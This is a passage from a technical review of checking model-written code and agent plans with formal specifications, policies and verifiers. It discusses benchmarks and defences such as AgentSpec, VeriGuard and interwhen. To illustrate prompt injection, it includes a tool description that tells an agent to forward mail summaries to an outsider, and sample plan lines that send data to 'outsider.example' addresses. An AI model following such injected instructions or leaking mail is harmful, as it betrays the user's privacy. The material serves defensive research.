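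Of the accepted programs, 94.7% had no postcondition. For these, Dafny had checked general conditions such as termination, but not whether the answer was right. Another 3.4% had a postcondition that did not refer to a separate specification, and only 1.9% had one that did. That share was similar on two other sets of Python problems, at 2.7% and 2.3%.

The system's prompt probably explains much of this, because it includes an example program that has no postcondition and gives its expected results in `expect` statements. Dafny assumes these statements are true during the proof and checks them only when the program runs. Vempaty and colleagues object to using the verifier's acceptance rate as a measure of correctness, but they do not regard this as a fault in the original system. Most of the programs worked, since 92.6% passed HumanEval's basic tests, but the proofs added little evidence of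 that.

The researchers caution that a specification can lack a reference to a separate definition without being empty. For a function that doubles a number, `ensures r == 2 * x` is a complete specification, yet it fails their check because it has no such reference. A postcondition can also pass the check and be worthless. In one of their examples, a function should return the largest number in a list, but the separate definition only requires a result that is not negative, so a program that returns 0 for [5, 3, 7] satisfies it.

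Vempaty and colleagues also built their own system, which rejects any component whose postconditions do not refer to the separate specification. Some of its fully verified programs still failed hidden tests:

| Benchmark | Fully verified programs | Failed hidden tests |
|---|---|---|
| MBPP-Rust | 1,080 | 124 (11.48%) |
| VeriContest, LeetCode problems | 1,545 | 229 (14.82%) |

The cause could be a poor specification, an error introduced in the translation from Dafny to Rust, or a wrong expected answer in the test. The researchers did not determine how often each of these happened.

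Of the 1,316 VeriContest programs that had both verified and passed the hidden tests, only 535 (40.7%) also had a precondition and postcondition that passed VeriContest's checks. The other programs appeared to work, but their proofs may have been about a different requirement from the one in the problem description.

### Models that write specification, code and proof

In May 2025, writing proofs looked like the main obstacle to getting a model to produce a verified program from a description. *VERINA* (Ye, Yan and colleagues, 2025) tested models on 189 programming tasks in Lean. The best general-purpose model, OpenAI's o3, wrote correct code for 72.6% of the tasks and a sound and complete specification for 52.3%, but a valid proof for only 4.9%.

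A year later, Xie and colleagues found a similar pattern on VeriContest, which uses Rust and the Verus verifier. The best model, GPT-5.5, had these success rates with one attempt per problem:

| Task | Success rate |
|---|---|
| Write the code from the description | 97.51% |
| Write the specification from the description | 57.16% |
| Prove that given code meets a given specification | 13.82% |
| Do all three from the description | 6.76% |

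Models that wrote correct code were not always good at writing specifications. GPT-5.4 mini wrote correct code for 83.90% of the problems but an adequate specification for only 7.85%.

The low proof score no longer reflects what models can do. Serbanuta and colleagues report that Claude Opus 5.5 proved all 1,325 theorems they derived from VeriContest's specifications and code, at a median cost of $1.20 per proof. They were testing their own company's tool, which uses Lean and allows up to 40 official checks per theorem, so the result is not directly comparable with a single attempt in Verus. Their agents also started from specifications that experts had reviewed.

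If proofs become routine, the quality of specifications will limit how often a model can produce a correct verified program. A model that writes an adequate specification for 57% of problems cannot produce a correct program verified against its own specification for more than 57%. Newer models may write better specifications than GPT-5.5 did.

*Self-Spec Verifiable Code Generation* (Qian, Dong and colleagues, 2026) tests models that must rely on their own specifications throughout. Its benchmark, VeriCodeBench, has 400 problems in C, Java, Rust and Python. For each problem, the model reads a description, writes a specification, and then writes code that must verify against it.

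Each problem also has a list of requirements that the model does not see. Software checks whether the model's postconditions imply the required ones and whether its preconditions allow every input that the requirements allow. Without the second check, a model could make its task easier by excluding difficult inputs. For example, a specification for totalling refunds might wrongly exclude the empty list.

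Across four models, an average of 71.0% of programs verified against the model's own specification, but only about 44% of all programs also had a specification that covered every requirement. So roughly 38% of the verified programs had a specification that left something out or excluded inputs it should have allowed.

Letting the model repair its code using the verifier's error messages does not correct the specification. On the C problems, repair raised the number of DeepSeek V3.2's programs that passed verification from 34 to 60 out of 100, but the number that also covered every requirement rose only from 8 to 11.

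Qian and colleagues also had the models list the requirements in ordinary language before writing the specification. The specifications then covered more of the requirements, but the programs were sometimes harder to verify. Kimi-K2.7-Code's average coverage on the Rust problems rose from 69.7% to 75.6%, while the number of its programs that were verified fell from 91 to 60. Someone who looked only at the verification rate would think the pipeline had become worse. Combining the list of requirements with repair gave the best overall result, with Claude Sonnet 5 succeeding fully on 65.5% of the problems.

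Some of these failures have causes other than misunderstanding the user. In *How Powerful Are LLMs in Generating Formal Program Specifications?*, Yang, Li and colleagues (2026) had six models write specifications for HumanEval problems in Rocq, a proof assistant, and tested each specification on correct and incorrect outputs. The best model, Gemini 3 Pro Preview, passed on 28.05% of the problems. The most common failure was invalid Rocq code, and specifications with valid syntax often described the right behaviour.

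That score probably understates the model's ability, because a specification passed only if a model could prove that it accepted the correct outputs. The best prover managed this for only 30.49% of even the specifications written by human experts. The study also gave the models a correct program along with each description, which left little room to misread the request, but a user asking for new software has no such program to supply.

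### Whether specifications can be cheap enough to check

Lahiri argues that an incomplete specification can still be useful. He recommends starting with the points where a model is likely to misread the request, and putting in more effort only when the program needs to be more reliable. For a small function, the user could approve a few tests. For a larger module, a model could propose a class invariant, a rule that a data structure must always obey. One well-chosen invariant can replace hundreds of specifications for separate functions, so the user has much less to review.

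His most ambitious example is 3DGen, which uses AI agents to translate the written standards for network data formats into a specialised specification language. Other software then generates a provably correct parser, a program that reads data in that format. 3DGen has produced parsers for 20 formats. Its task is unusually favourable because a detailed public document already describes what each parser should accept, and most requests to an agent come without such a document.

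Yang and colleagues write that producing a precise specification requires expert knowledge and often takes more effort than verifying the program. Their own specifications for HumanEval's 164 short functions took several person-weeks to write and review. Having a model draft the specification would avoid much of this work, but someone still has to check the draft. If the user approves only a few examples, she has settled what the program should do in those cases, but the rest of the specification is still the model's interpretation.

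A more basic objection is that much software has no complete specification that anyone could state. For example, nobody can write a formula that accepts every good summary of two contracts and rejects every bad one. Lahiri acknowledges part of this problem. Most of the research concerns small, self-contained functions, and he asks what a postcondition would mean for a machine-learning pipeline. Developers also spend most of their time changing existing programs, and users intend those changes to preserve behaviour that may not be written down anywhere.

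The benchmarks cannot show how much software this objection applies to, because they include only tasks that someone managed to specify. Xie and colleagues left out problems that needed decimal arithmetic or complex data structures. They also discarded problems that neither an agent nor an expert could verify within the time allowed.

Lahiri proposes specifying the parts that can be stated. In the contracts example, the user could require the summary to mention every clause whose text has changed. Software could check this rule and would catch a summary that omitted the new liability clause. It would not catch the program that compared the contracts in the wrong order, because its summary mentions the right clause but reverses the change. The user could add a rule about the direction of each change, if she thought of it. For a summary she needs only once, reading the changed clauses herself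 may be faster than writing and checking the rules.

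## Checking a plan against both policy and task before it runs

If an agent writes its whole plan before acting, software can check the plan against both a policy and a specification of the task. Meijer calls his version of this method "generate, verify, then execute". Java similarly checks a program's compiled code for memory and type errors before running it.

### How the checker finds a forbidden path

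Suppose a user asks an agent to fetch and summarise her mail. In Meijer's format, the plan is a list of steps in JSON, each with a tool, its arguments and a name for the result. Written as Python, it is:

```
emails  = fetch_mail()
summary = summarize_emails(emails)
return summary
```

As in CaMeL, an instruction hidden in a message cannot add a step to the finished plan, but a harmful step can come from elsewhere. In one of Meijer's examples, the description of the mail-fetching tool tells the model to send summaries of all mail to an outside address "for compliance reasons". A model that obeys would add a line before the last one:

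```
send_email("audit@outsider.example", summary)
```

Meijer's email policy, described earlier, treats the fetched mail as a source and the body of any message to an outside address as a sink. A plan breaks the policy if data can pass from the source to the sink. Meijer suggests finding such paths with CodeQL, a tool that searches programs for patterns. On this plan, the search has three steps:

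1. `emails` comes from the source, so the checker marks it.
2. `summary` is computed from `emails`, so the checker marks it too.
3. `send_email` has `summary` as its body and an outside address as its recipient, so the checker rejects the plan.

The checker can assess a plan without reading the messages, so the result holds for every inbox. It would reject even a plan that told an outsider only how many messages had arrived, because that number is computed from the mail. If the plan took the recipient from an address book, the address would not be available in advance, and the checker would have to reject the plan or leave that check until run time. Meijer expects some checks to remain for run time.

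The policy has to name the tools exactly. Meijer's printed rule calls the source `fetch_email`, but his plan uses a tool called `fetch_mail`. A checker that compared the names literally would find no source and accept the leak. A checker that tracks only data flow would also miss leaks through a plan's branches, and CaMeL's labels can miss them too.

### Adding a condition for the task

A plan that returns an empty summary without fetching any mail also obeys the policy. To exclude it, the user needs a specification. One part of it could be that the plan fetches the mail and passes every fetched message to the summariser:

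*for every message m in the result of fetch_mail, m is in the input of summarize_emails.*

The following plan obeys the policy but fails this condition:

```
emails  = fetch_mail()
recent  = emails[:10]
summary = summarize_emails(recent)
return summary
```

Suppose a plan sends nothing to anyone but summarises only the first ten messages in an inbox. To check the condition that every message is summarised, a verifier looks for an inbox that makes it false, and any inbox with 11 messages does.

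| Plan | Policy | Task condition |
|---|---|---|
| Summarises every message and returns the summary | Passes | Passes |
| Summarises ten messages and returns the summary | Passes | Fails |
| Summarises every message and also sends the summary to an outsider | Fails | Passes |

The task condition is incomplete, because a plan could satisfy it by summarising every message and then discarding the result. A fuller specification would also require the plan to return the summary. The condition also covers only fetched messages, so if `fetch_mail` returns just the latest 50, a plan can pass and still miss older mail.

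An administrator writes a single policy that covers every plan that uses the mail tools. The developer of each tool writes its contract and updates it when the tool changes. The user needs a new task condition for each new kind of request, but she can reuse the same condition if she wants the same summary every morning.

Even if the plan passes both checks, the summary may be inaccurate. The summariser is a language model, and its contract can guarantee that it returns text but not that the text is true. A malicious message can still mislead it, as with CaMeL's second model. Meijer suggests having the summariser label suspicious messages and adding ordinary filters, which may help but don't prove that the summary is accurate.

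### Systems that check a policy

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (Doshi, Hong and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that resolves conflicts in a user's calendar. The user's new appointment for treatment of a sexually transmitted disease clashes with a meeting. The agent moves the meeting and, although nobody has attacked it, reveals the appointment in its email to her colleagues.

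To find such hazards in advance, the researchers adapt a method that engineers use in aviation. They list the people whom the agent affects, what each of them values, and what the agent could do to harm it. For the calendar agent this leads to two rules:

- An email must not include event details that are private from its recipient, unless the user agrees.
- After each change to an event, the agent must email every attendee.

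The second rule requires an action, but it doesn't specify the user's task. An agent that moved the meeting to the wrong time and told everyone about it would obey both rules.

Doshi and colleagues modelled the agent in Alloy, a tool that searches every sequence of steps up to a fixed length. Alloy quickly found leaks without the rules but none with them, and the rules still allowed harmless sequences. The search doesn't rule out leaks in longer sequences, and the researchers had not yet built the software to enforce the rules on a working agent.

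*AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025) enforces rules on working agents, but it checks each action just before it happens instead of checking a whole plan. Each rule has a trigger, a check and a response. For example, when the agent is about to transfer money, one rule checks whether the recipient is a family member and, if not, prompts the user to confirm.

In one test, a simulated robot was told to fill a mug with water and pour it onto a laptop. AgentSpec stopped the robot at the last step, after it had filled the mug and found the laptop. Checking the whole plan could have stopped the robot before it moved. Across ten hazard categories, AgentSpec prevented every dangerous task, while the share of safe tasks completed fell from 58.62% to 54.26%.

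The paper also reports that AgentSpec stopped over 90% of unsafe code. In its table, an agent given 750 risky instructions tried to run 422 programs, and the rules flagged 333 of them, or 79%. The 90% figure seems to leave out two categories in which the code did not contain the flaw the agent had been asked to write. Without them, the rules flagged 333 of 364 programs, or 91%. The researchers then inspected the flagged programs and allowed 58 as harmless.

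People wrote those rules from descriptions of the risks in the benchmark. The rules that OpenAI's o1 model wrote for the robot caught only 70.96% of the hazards, although 95.56% of their warnings were correct.

### Proving that the checker is correct

The code that enforces a rule can contain mistakes, and *VeriGuard*, a system from Google (Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues, 2025), tries to exclude them by proof. A model turns a security request in ordinary language into a Python function that allows or denies actions, and writes preconditions and postconditions for it. The system asks the user about ambiguities, tests the function and uses the Nagini verifier to prove that it meets those conditions. It then applies the function to each action the agent proposes.

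The researchers attacked agents in several ways, including through prompt injections and planted memories. Without a defence, between 49.9% and 63.7% of attacks succeeded on average, depending on the model. VeriGuard reduced this to zero on all four models, but so did a simple guardrail that asked a language model whether each action obeyed the policy. The two differed in how many ordinary tasks the agent completed under attack:

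| Model | No defence | Simple guardrail | VeriGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 42.1% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56.7% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 43.1% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 89.0% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

VeriGuard's advantage may come from how it responds to a violation rather than from the proof. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, agents completed 38.1% of tasks when VeriGuard blocked the forbidden action. They completed 63.3% when it stopped only the offending tool call and told them which rule they had broken, so they could make a new plan.

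The proof also leaves two steps unchecked. A model writes the conditions, so Miculicich and colleagues say the user has to confirm that the conditions reflect what she meant. Another model extracts the function's arguments from the agent's output. If it extracts the wrong recipient for an email, a correct function can approve a forbidden message.

### Systems that check the task

Microsoft's *interwhen* (Bhat, Ekbote and colleagues, 2026) checks an agent's work against both the policy and the request, but during the run rather than before it. A model turns a policy document into small programs that inspect the agent's reasoning and tool calls as they appear. Any call that would change data is held back until it passes. If a check fails, the agent receives an explanation and tries again. After five failed corrections, it gives no answer.

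The researchers tested three sources of checks on 114 customer-service tasks for a telephone company, using the model Qwen3-30B. The first was the company's written policy. The second was a small set of earlier runs, which revealed rules the policy had left out or misstated. For example, the policy allowed the agent to add "at most 2GB" of data when the tasks required exactly 2GB. The third was the user's request, from which a small model worked out which tool calls the task needed.

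| Checks | Average score |
|---|---|
| None | 32.17% |
| Request only | 38.67% |
| Policy only | 42.11% |
| Policy and earlier runs | 71.10% |
| Policy, earlier runs and request | 87.70% |

Checking the request added 16.6 points even after the other checks were in place, which suggests that policy and task checks catch different mistakes. But the largest gain came from correcting the policy, and rules drawn from earlier runs may work better on this benchmark than on new tasks. The checks helped less on a harder benchmark, where a stronger model, GPT-5.4, improved only from 55.0% to 57.7%.

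Bhat and colleagues also tried checkers that were proved in Lean to match a formal version of the policy. These scored 83.77%, slightly less than checkers that people had reviewed. With the proof, nobody has to review the code, but a person still has to compare the formal policy with the written one.

Interwhen's task check only asks whether the expected tool calls occur. Astrogator verifies a complete script against a formal statement of the request before the script runs. Councilman, Fu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Formal Verification of LLM-Generated Code from Natural Language Prompts*, designed it for Ansible, a language for setting up and managing computers. The formal statement resembles English so that the user can confirm it:

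```
move file from remote "/scratch/file.txt" to remote "/home/user/data.txt"
```

Astrogator works out what the script would do, whatever state the computer starts in, and compares this with the statement. It also has a database of technical details, so the user can write "install numpy" without knowing that the package is named `python3-numpy` on Debian, a version of Linux.

The researchers had six models write 1,260 scripts for 21 tasks, and ran tests to decide which were correct.

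| Scripts | Accepted | Rejected |
|---|---|---|
| Correct (334) | 277 (82.9%) | 57 (17.1%) |
| Wrong (926) | 70 (7.6%) | 856 (92.4%) |

About 80% of the accepted scripts were correct. Most of the 70 wrong ones would have worked under assumptions that were false on the test computers, such as that a certain user account existed. Astrogator lists these assumptions, and in the full design the user would review them, but the experiment left out this review.

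Seven of the wrong scripts did more than the request allowed. One task was to create a file only if it did not exist, but some scripts overwrote the file every time. Another was to restart a computer if necessary, but some scripts always restarted it. As in the file-deletion example, the specification lacked a frame condition. Councilman and colleagues deliberately allow extra actions, because a user who wants to copy a project from GitHub may not know that the script must first install other software. A separate policy against overwriting files or restarting computers without approval could have caught these scripts without making the user's request longer.

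The systems cover different parts of what Meijer proposes:

| System | What it checks | Policy | Task |
|---|---|---|---|
| Meijer's proposal | The whole plan, before it runs | Yes | Yes |
| Doshi and colleagues' proposal | A model of the agent, then each tool call | Yes | No |
| AgentSpec | Each action, before it happens | Yes | No |
| VeriGuard | Each action, with a verified function | Yes | No |
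| Interwhen | Reasoning and tool calls during the run | Yes | Partly |
| Astrogator | The whole script, before it runs | No | Yes |

Only Meijer's proposal checks a whole plan against both, and he gives no measurements of how well it works.

### Where the method breaks

A false tool description can mislead either the model or the checker. If it leads the model to add a forbidden step, the checker can detect that step and reject the plan. If the description omits an effect, as with the file-writing tool that secretly reported metrics, the checker cannot detect it from the plan. Astrogator accepted one wrong script partly because an Ansible tool behaved differently from its documentation. Doshi and colleagues want every tool labelled with what it can do and how sensitive its data is, but they acknowledge that someone must first verify the labels. A company could use only tools from suppliers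 it trusts, or analyse each tool's code as Adam and colleagues do.

Some plans have to change once the agent has read the data. A user might ask the agent to deal with whatever is urgent in her inbox, and no plan written in advance can cover every message. CaMeL agents lost many tasks for this reason. The agent could instead read the mail, write a new plan and submit that for checking, but the new plan might contain this line:

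```
send_email("friend@outsider.example", "The merger closes on Friday")
```

The text came from the user's mail, but in the new plan it is a constant with no path from `fetch_mail`. To keep the guarantee, the checker would have to treat everything the model writes after reading the mail as private, and so block all outside messages, including the reply the user wanted. Interwhen checks each step as it comes instead of committing to a plan, but earlier steps may already have changed something by the time it finds a problem.

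Writing a specification for each request also takes a lot of work. The researchers wrote Astrogator's 21 formal statements by hand and had to describe the Ansible tools that the scripts used. That work is easier to justify for a script that runs every night on hundreds of computers than for a single inbox summary. Interwhen reduces the work by having a small model generate the task checks, but nobody confirms that the checks match what the user meant.

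### Guaranteed safe AI

All these checks depend on a description of what the tools do, which is a very small model of the world. Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues (2024), in *Towards Guaranteed Safe AI*, propose extending the method to the effects of an AI system on people and their surroundings. Their approach has three parts:

- A world model describes mathematically how the system's actions affect the world.
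- A safety specification states which effects are acceptable.
- A verifier proves that the system meets the specification according to the world model, or puts a limit on the probability that it does not.

The email policy can only forbid messages to certain addresses. A verifier with a good enough world model could also check what would happen after someone reads a message, such as whether following its advice would injure them.

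The proposal ranks world models by how much safety they would provide. A neural network that predicts outcomes but that nobody can inspect ranks near the bottom. Models of cause and effect that experts have fully audited rank higher, and models proved consistent with the laws of physics rank above those. One system could combine several kinds, such as a precise model of its sensors and a looser one of the people around it.

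The main objection is that nobody can prove the world model itself is right. A proof shows what follows from the model, but only observation can show whether the model matches the world, and the world may be too complex to model well enough. Dalrymple and colleagues give three replies.

Their first reply is that the guarantee can include the model's uncertainty. If the model is wrong with probability at most ε at each step, a plan of *n* steps that provably meets the specification in the model will meet it in reality with probability at least:

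*(1 − ε)ⁿ*

The model would have to be very accurate. If ε is 0.1%, the guarantee for 1,000 steps is only about 37%, and raising it to 99% requires an ε of about 0.001%. Someone also has to justify the value of ε from observations, which may not cover new situations.

Dalrymple and colleagues also argue that an AI system able to reliably carry out complicated and dangerous plans would show that accurate world models are possible. This is less convincing, because a planner only has to predict the results of the plan it chooses, while a safety proof has to cover every effect that could cause harm. People might also be unable to inspect the planner's model. Dalrymple and colleagues accept that a model of human behaviour may not be both accurate and understandable. They suggest listing a range of actions each person might take and proving the system safe for all of them, but if the range is wide,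 almost no useful action will pass that test.

Their strongest reply is that every method of making AI safe relies on assumptions about the world, and a world model at least makes them explicit, so people can examine them. Testing, for example, relies on future situations resembling the tested ones. This is a good reason to write the assumptions down, but they could still be false.

In 2026 the wider proposal was still a research goal. *Foundation World Models for Agents that Learn, Verify, and Adapt Reliably* (2026) sets out a vision of next-generation agents that learn world models suitable for formal proof. It also points to early methods that measure how far a simplified model departs from the original. *Towards Safe World Models* (Yu, 2026), a survey published in October, warns that accurate predictions alone don't make a world model safe to rely on, because errors in what the system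 observes, remembers or does can still lead to unsafe decisions. The approach is more practical where engineers can describe the surroundings by hand, as they already do for some aircraft controllers.
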